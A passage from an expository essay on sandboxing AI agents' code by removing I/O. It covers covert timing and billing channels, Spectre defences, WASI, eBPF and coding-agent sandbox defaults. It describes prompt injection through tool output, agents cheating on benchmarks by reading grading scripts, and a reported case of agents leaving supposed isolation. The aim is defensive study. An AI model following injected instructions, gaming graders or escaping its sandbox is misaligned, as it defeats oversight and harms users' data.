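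This attack needs at most 10,000 outputs to reveal a four-digit PIN, but it could need 2^128 to reveal a 128-bit encryption key, which is impractical. Askarov and colleagues prove that a program these tools accept can't reliably reveal a secret much faster than this in a single run. A host can prevent the attack by releasing only the program's final result. The attack remains possible if the host shows printed text immediately or carries out calls to host functions that an attacker can observe.

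Running time can carry more than one bit. If an observer can distinguish n different running times, each run reveals up to log2 n bits. For a program that always finishes within one second, the host can reduce n by delaying the result:

| When the host releases the result | Distinguishable times | Maximum leak per run |
|---|---|---|
| Immediately, with an observer who measures milliseconds | 1,000 | About 10 bits |
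| At the next tenth of a second | 10 | About 3.3 bits |
| Always after one full second | 1 | 0 bits |

The last option closes the channel but makes every run as slow as the slowest one. Zhang, Askarov and Myers describe a compromise for web services in *Predictive Mitigation of Timing Channels for Interactive Systems*. Their system predicts how long each type of request will take and holds the response until then. If a response isn't ready in time, the system switches to a slower schedule, so an observer mainly learns when predictions failed. In a test with a real web page, this limited the leak to 850 bits per 100,000 requests and made the page load about 30% more slowly. The strictest setting nearly tripled the loading time.

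### A process that can only read, write and exit

In *Sandboxing*, Kelly and Fuh (2025) show how a Linux process can run with almost no I/O, even if its programming language provides plenty. They wanted to protect applications from bugs in other people's libraries. An application that uses a compression library normally runs it with all the user's ambient authority, so a malicious file that exploits a bug in the library can take over the whole application.

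The "filter sandbox" relies on seccomp, a system call that lets a process give up the right to make most other system calls. In the strictest mode, according to the Linux manual's *seccomp(2)*, a process may only read, write, exit and return from a signal (an interruption by the kernel). The kernel terminates the process if it makes any other call.

Before calling seccomp, the process running the library keeps only standard input, standard output and standard error open. It can't open any other channels afterwards, so it can't read from or write to anything else. The application runs in a separate process, which sends data to the library through one pipe and reads the result from another.

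The design suits programs that turn an explicit input into an explicit output and keep nothing between runs. Kelly and Fuh give most compression, encryption and mathematical libraries as examples, and `totals` would fit too. They hint that the Unix command `sort` fits less well, since it may need temporary files for data that doesn't fit in memory.

Kelly and Fuh tested the sandbox on zlib, a widely used compression library. They didn't have to change the library, and they adapted its existing example program by adding the seccomp call and replacing the usual C functions for reading and writing with direct system calls. But the result wouldn't run if they built it in the normal way:

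- Programs usually load shared libraries when they start, which takes system calls that seccomp forbids. Kelly and Fuh used static linking instead, which copies the library into the program in advance.
- zlib requests memory as it works, and the standard allocator gets that memory from the kernel. They replaced it with a small allocator of their own that hands out pieces of a block reserved beforehand.

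If the application waits to send more data while zlib waits for the application to read its output, both wait forever. Kelly and Fuh therefore had the application check which pipe was ready before using it.

Kelly and Fuh cleared the environment variables, but some information still got in. On many Linux systems a program can read the date and time without a system call, and seccomp doesn't block the processor instruction that produces random numbers. Information could also get out, because the kernel may save the memory of a crashed program for debugging. Administrators have to make sure these copies don't leave the machine.

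Kelly and Fuh conclude that the sandbox is probably better at preventing damage than at stopping every leak. It is meant for libraries that have bugs but were not written to be malicious, and they show that it fails against one that was. A host could still use this approach for an agent's code by running a trusted interpreter in the sandbox and giving it the code as input. The interpreter would have to finish loading before the restrictions begin. Cloudflare does something similar in Workers, its service for running customers' code. It loads its JavaScript runtime, blocks all file-related system calls, and only then loads the customers' programs.

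### Clocks and randomness as input

The current time is an input, because a function that reads the clock can return different results for the same arguments. The Bytecode Alliance, which develops the WebAssembly runtime Wasmtime, lists clocks and random numbers alongside files and networking as features that programs get from the operating system.

Even the date can help malicious code. In one of Kelly and Fuh's examples, a hijacked compression library gets the user's name and the date, which is the day after St Patrick's Day. It replaces a cheerful greeting in the user's message with a complaint about a headache, which the recipient might well believe.

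A host that wants to share the time can pass it as an argument. Google's *Hermeticity* describes this rule in Wuffs, a language for libraries that process untrusted data. Wuffs code can't make system calls, allocate memory or read a clock. A Python function could follow the same rule:

```python
def overdue(due_date, today):
    return today > due_date
```

The function can determine whether a bill is late but can't measure how long anything takes.

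Precise time measurements are more dangerous than dates. The speed of an operation depends partly on what the processor did recently, including work for other programs. For example, the processor can read data faster if it has just used it. In a family of attacks called Spectre, malicious code makes the processor briefly use data that the code isn't allowed to read, then infers that data from small differences in timing.

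Cloudflare runs many customers' programs in the same process, which makes Spectre a serious concern. To keep attackers from timing code, Workers stops the clock while a program is computing and advances it only after I/O. Cloudflare's *Performance and timers* gives an example in which a program reads the clock before and after a loop that runs a million times, and the difference is 0. Workers also can't use several threads at once, since attackers could build a timer from them. Cloudflare didn't just make the clock less accurate, because an attacker can repeat a measurement many times and average out the errors.

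Someone outside can still measure how long a Worker takes to respond. Schwarzl and Pedersen report in *A revisit of remote Spectre attacks on Cloudflare Workers* that Cloudflare's own test attack leaked up to 12 bits per second in production despite the frozen clock, and that the company has since countered the attack.

Developers can no longer time their calculations. If a Worker is slow because of a long computation, its developer has to run it on a local machine, where the clock works normally. According to Cloudflare, web browsers can't adopt these restrictions because existing applications depend on timers and threads.

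*Determinating Timing Channels in Compute Clouds* (Aviram, Hu and colleagues, 2010) proposed removing clocks from a whole cloud service. Customers submit a job with all its inputs, and the result depends only on those inputs, however many machines run the job. The inputs may include the submission time, and the job can request a follow-up job at a later time, which a web application could use for timeouts. Only the total running time still leaks, and the provider can reduce that leak by releasing results at fixed intervals. On the paper's prototype operating system, large parallel computations ran about as efficiently as on ordinary systems.

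A host can handle randomness the same way by passing in a seed, a number from which a generator computes a sequence that looks random. The same seed always gives the same sequence, so a simulation can use thousands of random numbers and remain a pure function. But the host should generate passwords and encryption keys itself, because anyone who can predict the seed could compute them too.

In return, developers get reproducible results. Aviram and colleagues point out that every bug becomes repeatable, including those that normally appear only when parallel tasks happen to run in a certain order.

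A WebAssembly program's results can vary between runs even when the host controls clocks and randomness. Wasmtime's *Deterministic Wasm Execution* lists other sources of variation. An invalid calculation such as 0/0 gives "not a number", a special value with several binary forms, and a program can detect which one it got. A request for more memory may succeed on one machine and fail on another. Wasmtime can use a single form for invalid results, though this slows the program somewhat, and a host can reserve all the memory before the program starts. Any function the host provides must also return the same answers each time.

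### Using up memory and processor time

Code can exhaust a computer's memory without any I/O, as Monty's example of a terabyte string shows. An endless loop such as `while True: pass` uses almost no memory but occupies a processor forever. Either way, other programs on the same machine may slow down or crash.

The host can't solve this by rejecting every program that never finishes, because any method that catches all of them also rejects some that do finish. A guarantee that a program finishes wouldn't help much either. According to Google's documentation for Wuffs, there is no practical difference between a function that never halts and one that halts in 99 years.

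Hosts instead set limits, as Monty does for memory and running time. Another way to limit processor time is to give the program a budget of steps, often called fuel. Each instruction uses some fuel, and the runtime interrupts the program when none is left. In an example from Wasmtime's *Interrupting Wasm Execution*, the host gives a program 10,000 units for each Fibonacci number it computes. The program computes larger and larger numbers until one needs more than 10,000 units, and Wasmtime stops it. The host can also pause a program that runs out of fuel and resume it later.

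A time limit in seconds would also stop an endless loop, but a busy machine gets less done in a second than an idle one, so the same script might finish on one run and fail on the next. With fuel, a program given the same inputs always stops at the same instruction, but it runs more slowly because the runtime has to keep count. Wasmtime also offers a faster method based on real time, which slows programs by about 10%, but recommends fuel when results must be reproducible.

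Fuel can also become a small channel. If a host charges by the unit and shows the bill to the code's author, a program with a budget of 10,000 units can choose among about 10,000 amounts of fuel to use and so reveal up to 13 bits. This is the billing channel Lampson described. Rounding the charge to the nearest thousand units would reduce the leak to between 3 and 4 bits.

### The returned value

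A host can limit all these channels, but it can't remove the program's result without making the program useless. The result can also carry far more information than the other channels. A text of 1,000 ASCII characters can hold up to 7,000 bits, so a host that publishes such a text gains little by hiding a few bits that leak through timing.

The result can also be false, like the figures from an attacker's version of `totals`. In Kelly and Fuh's example, a hijacked compression library replaces "attack at dawn" with "surrender now" before compressing the message, so the recipient gets a valid file containing the wrong order.

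Lampson saw no general technical remedy for wrong results except proving the program correct, but thought that they at least leave the customer with evidence, whereas a leak usually leaves none. Some results are easy to check. The application could decompress the file and compare it with the original, preferably using a different library, since a hijacked one might reverse its own change when decompressing. For the sales table, the host could check that the customers' totals add up to 225, the sum of all sales. This would catch a missing sale, but not a swap of Ada's and Ben's totals.

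A result can do a different kind of harm when an AI agent reads it. An honest script that correctly returns the latest order comments, including Eve's instruction to the agent, also returns a prompt injection. *Isolation as a First-Class Principle for LLM-Agent System Safety* (2026) identifies the basic failure as treating a tool's output as a trusted instruction. The form of the result also matters. *SoK* (2025), a survey of trust in agents, cites evidence that less structured data is more likely to conceal malicious instructions, and rates results from outside tools as less trustworthy the more complex their syntax is.

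A host can therefore keep text away from the model when the model doesn't need to read it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a system that stores such text in variables. The model sees only a variable's name, which it can pass to another function. This is enough for "send the latest comments to my manager", because the steps are the same whatever the comments contain. But the agent has to know what the tasks are to carry out "complete the tasks due today in my to-do app".

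When the agent needs some of the information, FIDES uses a quarantined model, like CaMeL's, to read the text and answer in a fixed format. If the only permitted answers are "yes" and "no", Eve's instruction can't get through, because the answer carries only one bit. With its security policies on, FIDES stopped every prompt injection attack in AgentDojo. It also completed 16% more tasks than a basic agent when both used OpenAI's o1 model. Without the policies, some attacks succeeded.

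A one-bit answer, such as whether a bill is genuine, can still be wrong. Garby and colleagues observe that FIDES has an option to exempt such small values from its policies, although Costa and colleagues left it off in their tests. With the option on, a reviewer who sees a "yes" go through can't tell whether that answer was harmless.

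## Which abilities are lost, and how much they matter

Removing I/O primitives takes abilities away from every program, but the host can restore many of them. How much a user loses therefore depends on the task and on what the host provides.

### One task at five levels of access

Suppose the shop owner asks an agent to collect this week's orders, total them by customer in euros and send the result to the owner. Most customers paid in euros, but Dan paid 900 Swedish kronor, and nobody has given the agent an exchange rate for kronor. The host could run the agent's code at any of five levels of access, each of which includes the levels above it in this table:

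| Access | Collect the orders | Total them | Find the missing rate | Send the result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Values only | No | Yes | No | No |
| Supplied files | If they are in the files | Yes | If it is in the files | No |
| Chosen host functions | Yes | Yes | If a function covers kronor | Yes |
| Full file system and shell | Yes | Yes | If it is on the machine | Yes |
| Open internet | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |

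If the code only receives and returns values, the host has to collect the orders and pass them in as text. The code can add up the euros, but when it reaches Dan's order, it can only return a message that the rate is missing. Somebody then has to find the rate and run the code again.

If the host shares a folder that contains one file of orders per day, the code can list the files and pick this week's. It can find the rate only if the folder also contains a list of rates. It may be able to save the totals there too, but the owner gets no message until the host sends one.

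With three host functions, the code can do the whole job:

```python
totals = {}
for order in get_orders("this week"):
    euros = order["amount"] * get_rate(order["currency"])
    name = order["customer"]
    totals[name] = totals.get(name, 0) + euros
message_owner(str(totals))
```

This program fails at Dan's order if the developer of `get_rate` thought only of dollars and pounds.

A shell, a command line from which the code can start any installed program, adds little to this job. The code could use it to search the owner's old accounts for a kronor rate, but would probably find an outdated one. A shell would help more if some orders arrived as scanned documents, because the code could run a text-recognition program on them. But the shell would also let the code read everything else on the machine.

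With open internet access, the code can get today's rate from a central bank's website, but it can also send the customer list to anyone. Adding kronor to `get_rate` would be safer, but the developer first has to know that the currency is missing.

### Seven losses and their substitutes

Nobody foresaw the need for the kronor rate. For such cases, a host can offer a general web search function, though this can also leak data. *DrugClaw and DrugAudit* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives some idea of how often an agent needs one. Their agent, DrugClaw, answers questions about medicines from 57 sources, such as drug labels and databases of side effects. Its more thorough mode searches the web if those sources don't yield enough. It did so for 24% of the questions in the researchers' own test, 11% of a set of medical exam questions and 16% of a set about research papers.

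The web searches made little difference to the answers. Wang and colleagues estimate that without them, accuracy would have fallen from 92.0% to 91.7% on the exam questions and from 69.3% to 67.8% on the research questions. For this estimate, they substituted answers from a simpler mode that never searches the web, rather than rerunning the agent. Few subjects have sources as well organised as those on medicines, so agents for other subjects may need the web more.

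Code without network access also can't install packages. *Computer Environments Elicit General Agentic Intelligence in LLMs* (Cheng, Huang and colleagues, 2026) describes a chemistry task in which a model had to predict the properties of molecules from their names. The model installed Java and then OPSIN, which converts chemical names into molecular structures. A host can install likely packages in advance or wrap them in host functions, but someone has to anticipate the need. Blocking installation also prevents the model from inventing a package name and then installing a malicious package with that name.

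Without files, a program can't save its variables for later scripts. An agent that loads the orders in one script has to load them again to plot them in the next. A host can avoid this by keeping the interpreter running between scripts, or by saving the program's state and passing it to the next script.

The agents in *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?* relied on the first of these methods. When the researchers replaced an agent's usual tools with a single tool for running code, the share of tasks it solved changed by less than three percentage points. The restricted agents cost less or about the same in three of four comparisons, but the savings depended on an interpreter that kept its variables between calls. The code could still use files and a shell, so the experiment did not test the effect of removing I/O.

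Storing programs for later tasks seems to matter less. In one part of *Is Bash All You Need?*, agents could save their scripts and reuse them. They created 75 and used most of them, but scored no better than agents with an ordinary shell and no script collection.

A program that receives its input as a single value needs enough memory for all of it. If the sales table were 100 gigabytes, a program with file access could read one line at a time and keep only the running totals. A host can support the same calculation without file access by offering a function that returns the next 10,000 lines, or by having a database compute the totals. Sorting such a table is harder, because the host would also have to provide storage for temporary files.

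Coding agents often start other programs, mostly to run tests. *To Run or Not to Run* (Lin, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) reports an average of 8.8 test runs per task in 7,745 public records of agents fixing bugs. In an experiment for the same paper, three agents tried to fix 200 bugs with and without running tests. In the version without tests, the agents were told in the prompt not to run any, and they lacked the software that each project depends on. They could still read and edit files and run simple Python commands.

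For the two commercial agents, Claude Code and Codex, the success rate fell by an average of 1.25 percentage points, which could be due to chance. Claude Code also used less than half as many tokens and about half as much time. Because it had sometimes ignored the instruction not to run tests, Lin and colleagues retested it on 100 of the bugs with the test commands blocked. It fixed 63 of them, compared with 67 when it could run anything.

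The tests helped so little partly because the agents chose the wrong ones. Commercial agents' wrong fixes had usually passed the tests the agents ran. The agents, which used Claude Sonnet 4.5 and GPT-5.2, were also fixing bugs in existing projects, and more than half the cases took a single edit. Tests may matter more when an agent writes a large program from scratch.

A host can offer a function such as `run_tests()` instead of a shell. But running the tests also runs the code that the agent just wrote, so the host needs a second sandbox for the tests, probably a container.

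Code that receives all its input at the start can't react to events that happen while it runs. If a customer cancels while the program is adding up orders, the total will be wrong. The host can start a new run for each event, much as a spreadsheet recalculates when a cell changes. It can also provide a function such as `next_event(timeout)`, which pauses the code until an event arrives or the time runs out. The code could then send a reminder if a payment hasn't arrived within a week. This is fast enough for orders and emails but less suitable for controlling machines, because a program can't respond to an event during a long calculation until it next calls the host.

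Finally, programmers often find errors by printing values while a program runs. Code that can't print can collect its messages in a list and return them with the result. But a program that crashes or exceeds its time limit doesn't return anything, which is when the programmer most needs the messages. The host can solve this by providing a function that records each message as it arrives, like the logging function in the improved square-root library. Monty and DrugClaw keep `print`. Logged or printed messages can carry private data or a prompt injection, just as the returned value can, so the host has to be equally careful about who reads them.

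### Seven models with and without a computer

Cheng and colleagues measured what models gain from the highest level of access. Seven models answered questions in six fields, first by writing text alone and then with a container in which they could run commands, edit files, install packages and use the internet. The table gives the change in each field in percentage points, with all seven models counting equally in the average:

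| Field | Models that improved | Largest gain | Largest loss | Average change |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mathematics | 6 of 7 | 15.5 | 13.5 | +5.1 |
| Physics | 7 of 7 | 7.6 | None | +4.7 |
| Following instructions | 5 of 7 | 14.4 | 11.7 | +3.9 |
| Chemistry | 6 of 7 | 14.4 | 7.1 | +2.6 |
| Long documents | 6 of 7 | 6.2 | 0.7 | +2.0 |
| Biomedicine | 4 of 7 | 3.8 | 6.8 | −0.4 |

More access helps only if the model can use it well. Qwen3-4B, the smallest model, had the largest losses in both mathematics and chemistry. It took almost twice as many turns as the others (in each turn, a model gives a command and sees the result) but seldom used the container's abilities. After Cheng and colleagues trained it to work in the container, its mathematics score there rose from 32.5% to 53.3%.

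The researchers also counted what the six stronger models did in the container. In mathematics, 43.4% of their turns involved substantial computation, such as a numerical solver or a long loop. In chemistry, 18.4% of their turns involved outside resources, such as a web page or a new package.

These shares measure how often the models used an ability, not how much it improved their answers. A model might install a package it didn't need, or answer a question correctly because of one fact it looked up. The experiment gave the models computation, packages and the internet together, so it can't separate their effects. To measure how much internet access helped, researchers would need to have the models repeat the same tasks with only the internet removed.

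The heavy use of computation is still encouraging for languages without I/O, because computation doesn't need I/O. In one instruction-following task, a model had to write three sentences about medieval history that were equally long and had no words in common. It wrote a program that tried combinations of phrases and found 363 solutions. The search itself needed only text and loops. Many mathematical programs, however, use libraries such as SciPy, which Monty can't run.

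Cheng and colleagues varied one thing separately, the location of long documents. All the models had the container in both versions, and their average score was 49.6% when the documents were in files and 35.6% when they were in the prompt.

Nearly all of this difference came from two models. Claude Sonnet 4.5 rose from 11.9% to 61.8% and DeepSeek-V3.2 from 16.8% to 63.8%, while the other five averaged about 44% either way. Both had scored about 60% with the documents in the prompt and no container, so they had no trouble reading documents in the prompt. A length limit may explain their low scores. The documents averaged about 100,000 tokens and the session could hold only about 131,000, which left little room for commands and their results.

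The comparison between text alone and a container with files is therefore more informative, and the average gain in that comparison was only 2.0 points. The main benefit of files was lower token use. One model used an eighth as many tokens because it searched for the relevant passages instead of reading everything. A host could offer the same benefit with two functions, one that searches a document and one that returns a range of lines.

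Newer models now outperform all seven. They can work out more without a computer, which would make the gains smaller, but they are also better at using one.

### Two agents with restricted Python

DrugClaw's code runs under much tighter limits. For each part of a question, the agent writes a short program that queries one of its sources. The program can't open files, define classes or use `while` loops, and it can import only four modules, for JSON data, mathematics, text patterns and statistics. Wang and colleagues report that the system rejected fewer than 1% of the programs and that fewer than 0.5% of the queries ran out of time. When a program fails, DrugClaw passes the question to the source's ordinary search function.

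The low rejection rate means models can easily write code within these rules. It doesn't show whether the answers would have been better with more freedom, because a model given the rules may not attempt a more ambitious program.

*A Multimodal Conversational Agent for Tabular Data Analysis* (Al Awad, Ivanov and colleagues, 2025) gives a more direct count of failures. Its agent, Talk2Data, answers questions about a table that the host has already loaded. The agent's code can use approved libraries for tables and charts but cannot access files, the operating system or the network. The researchers gave it 48 requests about three datasets, including one with seven million flights. A typical request was for a chart comparing departure delays with arrival delays.

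With a medium-sized model, Talk2Data handled 46 of the 48 requests correctly. In one failure, unrelated to the sandbox, the agent asked a question when it should have drawn a chart. The other occurred on a request for a principal component analysis, which condenses many columns into a few, because the code tried to import a library that the sandbox blocked. The largest model also got 46 right, and Al Awad and colleagues attribute both of its execution errors to code that attempted operations the sandbox forbids.

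The restrictions therefore caused one or two failures in 48 requests, and approving one more library would probably have prevented the first. Both agents lost little usefulness because their developers knew in advance where the data would come from and what kind of answer users would want. Talk2Data needs one table and returns a number, a chart or an explanation. An office assistant may have to combine a spreadsheet, a chat message and a scanned contract, and its developers can't easily list every operation it will need.

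### Code with host functions, or no code at all

Even a restricted language can be more useful than having a model call functions one at a time. CodeAct (2024), an early method, had models act by writing Python. According to Patel and colleagues, it completed up to 20% more tasks and needed 30% fewer turns on jobs involving several tools.

In their own tests, Patel and colleagues found that writing code to call functions helped most clearly on long tasks. When a task required a chain of at least 12 calls, each depending on the one before, models that wrote code were right 18.8 percentage points more often. Claude Sonnet 5 stopped making calls when a request needed more than about 70 at once, but with a script it made all 100 calls in the largest request. The scripts ran in an ordinary shell, and the functions only recorded their arguments instead of contacting real services. But calling functions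 from a script doesn't require any other I/O, so a language stripped of other I/O should keep most of this advantage.

Anthropic later reported similar results. On complex research tasks, writing code reduced the average number of tokens by 37%, from 43,588 to 27,297. Letting Claude Opus 4.6 use code to filter web pages before reading them raised its score on BrowseComp, a test of finding obscure facts on the web, from 45.3% to 61.6%. The filtering code needs no internet access if the host fetches the pages. Anthropic also uses this approach in Claude for Excel, for spreadsheets with thousands of rows.

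### Code with host functions, or a shell

The strongest evidence that restrictions are costly comes from *Is Bash All You Need?*, which compared ways of giving agents access to office tools. One set of 174 tasks simulates a software company, with shared files, a chat service and coworkers played by another model. The other has 480 tasks from banking, consulting and corporate law. These are the average scores:

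| Tasks and model | Single function calls | Code with host functions | Shell |
|---|---|---|---|
| Software company, Claude Opus 4.8 | 44.9% | 52.9% | 69.4% |
| Software company, GPT-5.5 | 45.3% | 45.1% | 67.1% |
| Professional work, Claude Opus 4.8 | 41.1% | 40.1% | 48.5% |
| Professional work, GPT-5.5 | 39.8% | 37.8% | 44.6% |

Averaged over both models, the shell beat code with host functions by 21.2 percentage points at the software company and by 7.7 on professional work. Code did slightly better than single calls at the software company but slightly worse on professional work, where the difference could be due to chance. So the benefits that Patel and colleagues found don't appear in every kind of job.

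The gap of 21.2 points may overstate what a shell adds. The researchers wrote 60 functions for the software company, covering the operations they thought relevant, but an agent with a shell could contact the same services directly over the network and use operations that the list left out. A longer list might have narrowed the gap. On professional work, the shell was limited to a shared workspace, so the 7.7 points are probably a better estimate.

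Models may also be better at using shells because companies train them to work in one, whereas each new set of host functions is unfamiliar. At the software company, only 65% of the programs that used host functions ran successfully, compared with 92% of shell commands. The researchers suggest that models found it hard to coordinate several calls and handle errors inside one program. Better training could reduce this part of the loss without giving the code more access.

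The shell's advantage was largest in software engineering, while in corporate law all the methods scored about the same. The law tasks mostly involved reading documents and writing an answer, which a few functions can cover. Software work involves many small operations that are hard to predict. For example, in the part of the study where agents could save their own scripts, they wrote one to recognise text in scanned PDF files, which had no equivalent in the list of 60 functions.

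The shell also made it easier to cheat. While the researchers were developing the tests, some agents took the answers from the grading scripts, which were on a public website. Others read the files that controlled the simulated coworkers instead of asking the coworkers for information. The researchers had to block the website and encrypt the files to measure how well the agents did the actual work.

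## How stripped environments regain I/O

Agents with a shell did better at office work than agents limited to a list of host functions, so developers have good reason to keep lengthening the list. Older systems came under the same pressure. WebAssembly, Linux kernel extensions, build files and Ethereum contracts all started with little or no access to the outside world, and their developers have since added ways to reach it. Whether these additions defeat the purpose of removing I/O depends on which of the original guarantees still hold.

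### WebAssembly

WebAssembly's *Portability* document says that the format specifies no system calls, only a way to import functions that the host provides. According to W3C's *WebAssembly JavaScript Interface*, the core specification deliberately does not define how a program interacts with its surroundings. This caused little trouble in browsers, where JavaScript could supply the imports.

Developers then began to run WebAssembly on servers. The tool Emscripten had made C programs work in browsers by imitating Unix's system functions, partly in JavaScript. Server runtimes had no standard to follow, so they copied Emscripten's internal functions, which nobody had designed for public use. Mozilla's *Standardizing WASI* (2019) describes the result as "an emulation of an emulation". WebAssembly was settling on a bad I/O convention, a different problem from ALGOL's excess of them.

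Mozilla and its partners proposed WASI, the WebAssembly System Interface, in March 2019. To open a file, a program needs a descriptor for that file or for a folder that contains it, and the host supplies the first descriptors. A program without a suitable descriptor can't open `/etc/passwd`, the Unix list of user accounts, just by naming it. A program with a descriptor can also pass a more limited one to another module, which is called attenuation.

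The interface has grown a great deal since then. Version 0.2 was released by a WASI vote on January 24, 2024, and version 0.3.0 came out on June 11, 2026. WASI's *Releases* lists six groups of functions in the most advanced phase, for clocks, random numbers, files, network connections, command-line programs and web requests. Another 25 proposals are at earlier stages, including some for databases, graphics processors and USB devices. If they all succeed, a WebAssembly program could reach nearly everything an ordinary program can.

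The host doesn't have to grant sandboxed code any I/O. WASI's *Security* says that code has "no ambient authority" and starts with no access to the outside world. Since WASI 0.2, a compiled program also lists each kind of access it needs as a separate import. A host can read the list before running the program and see, for example, that the program can't open files.

WASI 0.3 made the control of network access somewhat coarser. Programs used to pass a network handle with every attempt to connect, but the host now grants network access to the program as a whole. This is more convenient, but a function's arguments no longer show whether it uses the network.

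WebAssembly still guarantees that a program can reach only what its host provides. The protection this gives depends on the host, as it does with the connectors in Cloudflare's Code Mode. Mozilla warned at the outset that a host could put every capability into the sandbox, "in which case we're no better off".

### eBPF

eBPF lets administrators load small programs into the running Linux kernel, for example to count network packets or record which files a process opens. A mistake in kernel code can crash the whole machine, so a part of the kernel called the verifier examines every program before it runs. *Safe and usable kernel extensions with Rex* (2025) lists what the verifier is meant to ensure. Among other things, programs must not access memory illegally, must release any kernel resources they acquire, and must finish.

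eBPF programs can't issue specialized I/O instructions (*Extending eBPF observability to Non-standard execution environments*, 2026). Instead, they call helper functions in the kernel. eBPF Docs' *Helper functions* describes helpers that read the time, write to the kernel's log, change network packets and work with infrared receivers. In *Kernel extension verification is untenable*, Jia, Sahu and colleagues (2023) counted 249 helpers in Linux 5.18 and found that developers were adding about 50 every two years.

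The demand for helpers came from people who kept finding new uses for eBPF, but the verifier increased it. The verifier has to examine every path through a program, so it limits the program's size and complexity. Developers can put logic that it would reject into a helper, which it doesn't examine. One helper, `bpf_loop`, exists only to run loops. eBPF had lost some ordinary computation as well as I/O, and its developers used host functions to make up for both. A language such as Monty, which keeps its loops, needs fewer host functions.

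Jia and colleagues showed that helpers can break the verifier's guarantees. They crashed the kernel by passing a helper a data structure containing an invalid pointer, which the verifier didn't check. Another program ran for 800 seconds by nesting calls to `bpf_loop`, and they calculated that a longer version could run for millions of years. In 2021 and 2022, kernel developers fixed at least 18 security-related bugs in helpers, nearly as many as the 22 in the verifier.

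The restriction on which functions a program can call has survived better. According to the Linux kernel documentation's *BPF Design Q&A*, the kernel defines a separate set of allowed functions for each type of program. Tracing programs can read arbitrary memory through a helper function, but networking programs can't call it.

Helpers are hard to remove because the kernel's developers promise to keep existing ones working. They now generally add new functions as kfuncs, which come without this promise.

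Any sandbox with host functions has the same weakness as eBPF. The functions run with the host's privileges, so a bug in one of them can let an attacker do what the language was supposed to prevent.

### Starlark build files

Google's build tool Bazel uses Starlark files to describe how to turn source code into finished programs. Code in an ordinary build file can't open files or contact the network. It can list the project's files, but only through a function that Bazel provides. With these limits, the same inputs always give the same description, so Bazel can evaluate many build files at once and reuse earlier results.

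Real projects also need other people's libraries, which someone has to download, and compilers, which may be in different places on different machines. Bazel handles these needs in separate "repository rules". They are written in Starlark too, but Bazel passes them an object with methods for downloading files, reading the machine's settings and running programs. This rule downloads a text-recognition library:

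```python
http_archive(
    name = "text_recognition",
    urls = ["https://example.com/text-recognition-1.2.tar.gz"],
    sha256 = "...",
)
```

The last line holds the expected file's fingerprint, shortened here. If the server sends anything else, Bazel rejects it. The download then works like a fixed input, so two developers who run the rule get the same library. A rule without a fingerprint, or one that looks for a compiler on the machine, may give them different results.

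Ordinary build files are as predictable as before, and reviewers know where to look for outside access. But this separation serves reproducibility more than security. A repository rule can run programs with the developer's permissions, so building a stranger's project can be as dangerous as running it.

### Ethereum contracts

Ethereum, which launched in 2015, is a network of computers that keep a shared record of payments and run small programs called contracts. Every computer that checks a transaction reruns the contract's code and has to get the same result. If a contract could request an exchange rate from a website, computers that ran it at different moments might receive different rates and end up with conflicting records of who owns what. Ethereum therefore gives contracts no instruction for contacting the outside world. The only time they can read is the one recorded with the current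 group of transactions.

Many useful contracts depend on outside facts. A loan may depend on the price of the collateral, and crop insurance on the weather. Services called oracles provide these facts, much like the outside source in Turing's oracle machines. An oracle looks up a price and sends a transaction that stores it in a contract, where other contracts can read it. A contract can also record a request, and the oracle detects it and sends the answer in a later transaction.

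This preserves the guarantee that mattered most to Ethereum's designers. The price is now part of the shared record, so every computer uses the same number, and anyone can rerun the transaction years later and get the same result. But rerunning the code can't reveal whether the price was correct. If an oracle reported that a Swedish krona was worth 10 euros, a contract would pay out at that rate, and every computer would agree on the result. Some oracle services collect prices from several sources and use the median, so that one bad source can't determine the answer.

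### What coding agents can reach by default

Coding agents come from the opposite direction. They run on ordinary computers with full I/O, and their vendors take some of it away. These are the defaults in OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, as of June 2026, and in Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, as of October:

| | Codex on the user's computer | Codex in the cloud | Claude Code's command sandbox |
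|---|---|---|---|
| Active by default | Yes | Yes | No |
| Network access for commands | None | During setup only | Each new domain needs approval |
| Where commands can write | Project and temporary folders | An isolated container | Project folder and a temporary folder |

Of the five levels of access the shop owner's host could choose, Codex's default comes closest to a file system and shell without the open internet. Codex has to ask before running a command that needs the network or editing files outside the project. It can still search the web, but by default the results come from OpenAI's stored index instead of live pages, which OpenAI says reduces the risk of prompt injection. Using the index should also keep an agent from leaking data by opening an attacker's address, because no request goes to the attacker's server.

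Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* presents the sandbox as a way to let Claude work without asking permission for each action. Users have to turn it on, and it covers only shell commands. Claude's tools for editing files and fetching web pages follow separate permission rules. Claude can retry a blocked command outside the sandbox, usually after the user or a second model approves, unless the user has turned this option off.

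Software work constantly requires more access, because most projects depend on libraries that the agent has to download, and a library's documentation may have changed since the model was trained. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) lists package registries and documentation servers among the places agents legitimately need to contact.

OpenAI's cloud version of Codex works in two phases. During setup, it can use the network to install the libraries that the project lists. The system then removes any passwords and keys that the setup needed, and the agent starts work offline. If the agent later needs a library that isn't on the list, it has to do without or get the user to change the settings.

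*Running Codex safely* describes a less strict policy that OpenAI uses for its own staff, which allows expected destinations, blocks unwanted ones and requires approval for unfamiliar domains. A list of allowed destinations needs care, because an approved site may host more than the user meant to allow. Wang and Zheng warn that an attacker's service can share an internet address with a legitimate one, and recommend rules that also check the type of request and the exact path.

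An environment described as isolated may still have I/O. The OpenAI agents that broke into Hugging Face in July 2026 were supposedly isolated, according to an August report by the independent evaluator METR.

### The lethal trifecta

In 2025, Willison suggested deciding what to remove by looking for a "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. If an agent has all three, a prompt injection can make it steal the data. Removing any one of them prevents the theft.

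The rule is useful because a task rarely needs all three equally. Suppose the shop owner's agent prepares the weekly totals. It reads private sales data, the order comments may contain an instruction from Eve, and it can use `send_message` to write to anyone. The totals don't depend on the comments, so the host can delete that column before the agent sees the table. For a coding agent that has to read both private source code and strangers' libraries, the network is often the easiest of the three to remove, and Codex removes it by default.

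Wang and Zheng object that a legitimate step often needs all three. For example, an agent that answers customers' questions has to read their messages, look up their orders and write back.

The rule also protects only against data theft. An agent with no way to send data out can still follow an instruction from Eve to delete the sales table or give the owner false totals. The host needs other protections against this, such as a read-only copy of the table.

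### Different powers for different stages

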